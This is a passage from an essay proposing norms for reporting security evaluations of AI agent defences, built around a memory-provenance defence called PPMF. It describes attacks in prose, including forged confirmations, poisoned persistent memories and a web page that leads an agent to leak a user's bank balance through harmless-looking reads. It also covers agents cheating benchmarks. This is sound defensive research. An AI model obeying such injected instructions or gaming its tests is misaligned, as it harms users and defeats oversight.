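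| The gate links each call to the right memories | PPMF's matching code, and whoever maintains the list of aliases | 100 cases with aliases, partial matches and unrelated confirmations | Unclear match: closed. Wrong entry in the alias list: open (inferred) | Unclear match: no attacks succeed. Wrong alias entry: not measured |
| The agent retrieves the memory that holds the confirmation | The memory search | Added 20 decoy memories to each case | Closed | 79.4% of legitimate actions work if the search returns 10 memories, and 99.0% if it returns 20 |
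| Every high-risk call passes the gate | Whoever installs PPMF | Not tested | Open (inferred) | Not measured |
| Nobody tricks the user into confirming | The user, and whoever designs the approval screen | Not tested | Open (inferred) | Not measured |

A deployer should probably start with the last two rows, because both assumptions fail open, depend on the deployer's own set-up, and have not been measured. The risk labels come next, since so many real tools have missing or copied safety hints. The row on memory search shows that PPMF can also block a fifth of legitimate actions, even if every label is correct, because the agent did not find the right memory.

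Xu and colleagues' appendices already contain a similar table for failures that block legitimate actions. It lists each failure's mechanism, measured effect and remedy, such as tying every confirmation to a particular target and class of risk. The failures that let attacks through, which a deployer most needs to find, are in another table with only a short note on each.

The 8.8% and 11.2% figures come from corrupting a random tenth of the labels, so authors should also report how often attacks succeed in the cases with corrupted labels. For forged confirmations, that rate is probably close to 100%, which is much more useful to a deployer than 8.8%.

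### Evidence and assumptions

Verbs like "enforces" and "prevents" can describe a theorem, a test result or a design goal. Authors can avoid this ambiguity by sorting their claims under three headings. For PPMF, the main entries would be:

- Proved: an appendix sketches a proof that a claim from an untrusted source cannot by itself authorise a high-risk call, unless the platform has recorded a confirmation for that action. It is a sketch, and no proof checker has verified it.
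- Measured: no attack succeeded in the tests with correct labels, and every confirmed action went through except in the tests with decoys. In one pilot, PPMF added about 0.15 milliseconds per case.
- Assumed: everything in the table above.

*PerMIT* is the best precedent because it also lists the differences between the model on paper and the one the proof checker verified. If an agent paper's prototype differs from its theorem, as *PACE*'s does, the paper should report the difference under the first heading.

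The fourth norm follows PACT, whose designers tested it with correct labels and then with automatic ones. Ideally both tests use the same tasks. PPMF has results only with correct labels. Xu and colleagues call their tests with missing labels a test of "non-oracle operation", but deleting correct labels at random is a poor substitute for a real labelling system, which would also get some labels wrong. Authors who have no such system can write "not tested" in the second column.

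### The attacker, and the harms left out

An attack success rate is close to meaningless without the number of attempts, because the rate can rise sharply with more attempts. Claude Opus 4.5's rose more than tenfold between one attempt and a hundred. Authors should also say whether the attacker knows the defence and the policy, whether they see the result of each attempt, and how much money, computing power or skilled labour they have.

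Several recent surveys make similar recommendations. *Connecting the Dots in Agentic AI Security* (Baek, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026) recommends that tests of defences specify the attacker's knowledge, access and budget, and whether the attacker adapts. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) recommends reporting separate results for attackers who ignore the defence and attackers who adapt to it. *SoK* (2026), which covers attacks on agents through their tools, suggests a fixed budget for each route of attack, such as 100 trials, and counting a case as a success for the attacker if any of several runs succeeds.

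A label such as "adaptive" is not enough to describe an attack. PPMF's paper uses it for one of its sets of 30 attacks, but Xu and colleagues built that set from templates with more indirect wording. They do not describe an attacker who revises a text after PPMF blocks it. A sentence such as "one fixed text per case, with no revision" would have made this clear. Papers could also use shared terms for attackers' goals, capabilities and knowledge, such as those Hamin (2026) defines in *Adversarial Machine Learning*, a draft from the US standards agency NIST.

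Exclusions are easier to understand with an example. Xu and colleagues say that PPMF does not fully cover chains of low-risk actions that add up to serious harm, but a reader may not see what this allows. Suppose an attacker's web page contains a note telling the agent to look up the user's bank balance and then search the attacker's site for that number. PPMF classes both calls as reading, which needs very little trust, so its rule would allow both. The attacker would learn the balance, but the test would not count this as a successful attack because neither call is high-risk.

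Chu's survey sets a precedent by giving a combination of defences for each of seven kinds of attack, with a column listing the risks that remain. Designers can use that column to decide which defence to look for next. For indirect prompt injection, for example, one remaining risk is an attack that persists in the agent's memory, which is the problem PPMF was designed to solve.

### Numbers and versions

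Readers can use a count and an interval to judge how much evidence is behind a zero, and benign success to judge whether the agent still works. Chu complains that most published tests leave out how often a defence blocks legitimate actions, and gives the example of a defence that stops 95% of attacks but blocks 40% of legitimate actions. An invoice agent with that defence would fail to pay 20 of every 50 genuine invoices.

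A paper should also define what counts as a successful attack. Baek and colleagues distinguish three levels: the attacker changes what the model writes, changes what the agent decides to do, or causes a verified change in an outside system. PPMF's tests used different definitions. In the web sandbox test, which had only 20 attacks, an attack succeeded only if it changed something on a local server. The larger test, with 1,824 malicious pages, used a weaker measure of harm, because an attack succeeded if the gate authorised the action.

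An average can also hide the attacks that matter most. CAISI reports results separately for each of its five attack goals, which range from sending a harmless email to downloading and running a malicious script. An agent that sends the email but doesn't run the script is safer than one that does the opposite, yet the two could have the same average.

An interval applies only to the kind of trial that produced it. *Limits of Statistical Assurance for Embodied and Agentic AI under Adaptive Adversaries* (2026) models an attacker who tries to cause as many failures as possible after a system has passed a statistical test. One of its reference values is an upper limit of 16.8% on the violation rate for AgentDojo's banking tasks, based on 20 runs with no violations. Nobody attacked the agent in those runs, so the limit doesn't bound what an attacker could achieve. Authors should state next to each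 interval what kind of attacker, if any, took part.

The last norm concerns how long a result stays valid. Xu and colleagues list the versions of Python and the other software they used, which helps someone who wants to rerun the experiments. A deployer needs to know something else, namely which changes make the result unusable. For PPMF, the answer would be roughly this:

- Replacing the model that writes the memories does not void the guarantee. Xu and colleagues tried six such models, and no attack passed the gate with any of them.
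- Adding a tool voids it until somebody gives the tool a correct risk label.
- Relaxing the policy, for example so that user history can authorise emails, voids it for those emails.
- Changing the memory search leaves the guarantee intact but voids the figures for legitimate actions.

A defence that depends on the model's behavior would need a much stricter first entry, because any update to the model could change the result. Baek and colleagues add that an agent's surroundings affect what it does, so researchers should record its permissions, initial memory and tool versions as well as the model.

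### What existing guidance covers

*Measuring Security Without Fooling Ourselves* (Abdelnabi, Hicks and colleagues, 2026) discusses an earlier step, checking that a benchmark measures what it should. It focuses mainly on agents that search for security flaws, which may find it easier to break into the test software and read the answers than to solve the task. It cites an audit in which agents could do this on every task of some widely used benchmarks, including SWE-bench and Terminal-Bench.

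Abdelnabi and colleagues propose planting canaries, random values that an honest agent has no reason to read, so that an agent that repeats one reveals that it cheated. They also suggest giving an agent a fixed budget, such as $10,000, to try to cheat. If it fails, the benchmark's scores are more likely to reflect real ability, though they stress that this is not a guarantee. They want researchers to run each task several times and report the worst result, the variance and the number of critical failures, as well as the average.

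These proposals fit the eight norms. A table of assumptions should include a row for the benchmark, such as "the scoring code detects every successful attack". Yin found 11 attacks that AgentDojo's official checks had missed, so that assumption was false for AgentDojo. Abdelnabi and colleagues also warn that benchmarks become outdated. Researchers kept using intrusion-detection datasets from the 1990s for over a decade, although the data was obsolete within two years. A paper should therefore report the benchmark's date alongside the versions.

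The surveys concentrate mostly on attackers and metrics. Only seven of the 22 attack studies that Baek and colleagues examined tested a defence, though they selected studies with public code or data, so the share may differ elsewhere. None of the ten benchmarks Chu examined tested attacks that last from one session to the next. Baek and colleagues' later survey includes one that does, AgentLAB, which plants a malicious memory and exploits it in a later scenario. Chu recommends at least five changes of session between planting such an attack and triggering it. PPMF's main tests have one such change, although an appendix reports a longer test.

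The template in *Towards trustworthy agentic AI* (2026) comes closest to being complete. It includes a description of the system, a threat model, the test scenarios, the thresholds for release, the results with 95% intervals, the conditions for withdrawing the system, and the prompts given to any model that judges the results. But neither this template nor Chu's five recommendations cover the assumptions behind a result or the effect of breaking them. Systems security and a few agent papers, such as PPMF's, provide better precedents for reporting these.

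Official guidance is still developing. NIST's *Towards Best Practices for Automated Benchmark Evaluations* announced a draft, AI 800-2, in January 2026. The draft covers agents as well as language models and has a section on analysing and reporting results. In July, NAAIMES, a network of ten members including the United States, the United Kingdom and the European Union, published guidance that builds on the draft. *Automated Evaluation of Large Language Models* (2026) tells evaluators to define exactly what they are measuring and to acknowledge what they exclude, which is half of the sixth norm. However, it doesn't cover adversarial testing, tests of agents or the interpretation of results, so it would not help much with a paper like PPMF's.

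Two other NIST publications cover parts of the problem. According to the news site ExecutiveGov, NIST's *Expanding the AI Evaluation Toolbox with Statistical Models* responds to benchmark reports that rely on implicit assumptions, mix up different measures of performance or fail to quantify uncertainty. That supports the seventh norm and, more loosely, the second. The draft on terminology focuses on attacks on agents, and NIST's *Adversarial Machine Learning* (2026) bulletin invites comments until 18 December 2026. NIST, NSA and CISA's *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response* (2026) covers agents that exceed their instructions during training and testing, not how to report a defence's results.

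### Objections

Some authors will fill in the table with boilerplate, as many did in early Internet standards. The columns make this harder, because "the platform is trusted" leaves out who makes it true and how anyone checked. Reviewers can treat a row as too vague if it could appear unchanged in any other paper on agent security. An honest "not tested" is useful, because the deployer then knows what to test.

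Conference papers have strict page limits, and PPMF's table would take up perhaps half a page. Most of its content was already in the paper, spread over several appendices, so the main work is moving it. If space is short, exact software versions can stay in an appendix or with the code, but the conditions need to be in the main text because many readers never open the appendix.

The most serious objection to these norms is that reviewers will punish candour, so an author who follows them alone may be at a disadvantage. A paper that reports 8.8% attack success with forged confirmations may look weaker than one that reports zero but never tried forging any. A conference could reduce the problem by requiring the table from every paper on a defence and marking papers down for missing rows but not for bad results. Every defence has assumptions, even if the paper doesn't list them, so the conference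 could also tell reviewers to judge whether an assumption is realistic and well tested instead of marking a paper down for having one.

The table tells attackers where to look, but an attacker who reads PPMF's rule can already see that a forged confirmation would defeat it. Publishing working attacks is riskier than publishing assumptions, and researchers often accept that risk. For example, *The Devil is in the Context* argues that the benefit of better evaluation outweighs the danger of someone reusing its attack cases. Xu and colleagues ran their attacks only against local servers and planned to remove secrets and usable attack code before release. Authors should be more careful with flaws in a particular product. A paper should say that its guarantee fails if a plug-in can write to the log, but if the authors discover that one company's plug-ins can do this today, they should tell the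 company before publishing that.

**Nobody can list an assumption they haven't thought of.** No reporting rule would have led He and colleagues to write down that a Wi-Fi device installs each key only once. But a list makes missing assumptions easier to find, because any attack that succeeds while every listed assumption holds must exploit an unlisted one. Authors could adapt Abdelnabi and colleagues' cheating budget and pay outsiders to look for such an attack before publication. They would report the amount spent and the result, adding a row to the table for each attack that worked. If the outsiders found nothing for $10,000, that would be some evidence that the list is complete, though only against attackers with similar skills and budgets.

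### What the norms cannot fix

A complete table can still contain bad evidence. Testing an assumption with a weak attack makes the number in the last column too low, and the people who fill in that column usually built the defence. Reviewers rarely have time to rerun the experiments. Public code helps, but Baek and colleagues point out that releasing it does not mean anyone has reproduced the results.

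The norms also can't stop others from dropping the conditions. A journalist or a sales team can shorten the improved abstract to "PPMF blocked all 629 attacks", which is true but leaves out nearly everything a deployer needs. The authors can at least use the full sentence in their own talks and posts.

A table in a paper describes the authors' system. It shows that forged confirmations are dangerous, but not whether a particular company's staff or plug-ins can forge one.

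### Who could enforce them

Reviewers are the obvious people to enforce the norms about wording. They can compare an abstract with a table of assumptions in a few minutes, without special equipment. If the abstract reports a zero and the table lists author-supplied labels, the reviewer can ask for that condition to be added to the abstract. But reviewers see a paper only once, before publication, and never see most company announcements.

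Benchmark maintainers could enforce the norms about numbers more easily, by making the submission form require the number of attempts, the type of attacker, benign success and exact versions. They could also publish a standard set of corrupted labels. Authors would then not have to design their own sensitivity tests, and readers could compare how badly two defences fail under the same errors. This would probably help more than any other single step, because each paper now breaks different assumptions in different ways, if it breaks any.

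Buyers have the most influence over vendors, who don't need a reviewer's approval to publish a claim. NIST's announcement of AI 800-2 lists procurement specialists among the people who use evaluation reports. The law firm Pillsbury says NIST's work on agent standards may lead to guidance that influences what buyers require and how they vet vendors. NIST also accepts proposals of this kind. In a January 2026 Federal Register notice, CAISI asked for information on securing agents and said the responses may inform its guidelines on measuring agent security.

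A buyer doesn't have to wait for those guidelines. Before signing a contract, a company could ask the vendor to fill in the table for the product it is selling, naming the buyer's staff in the rows that depend on them. The contract could require the vendor to give notice before making any change that would void the result. A small company may not have the bargaining power to get that clause, but it can still ask for the table and treat a refusal as a reason to do its own testing.
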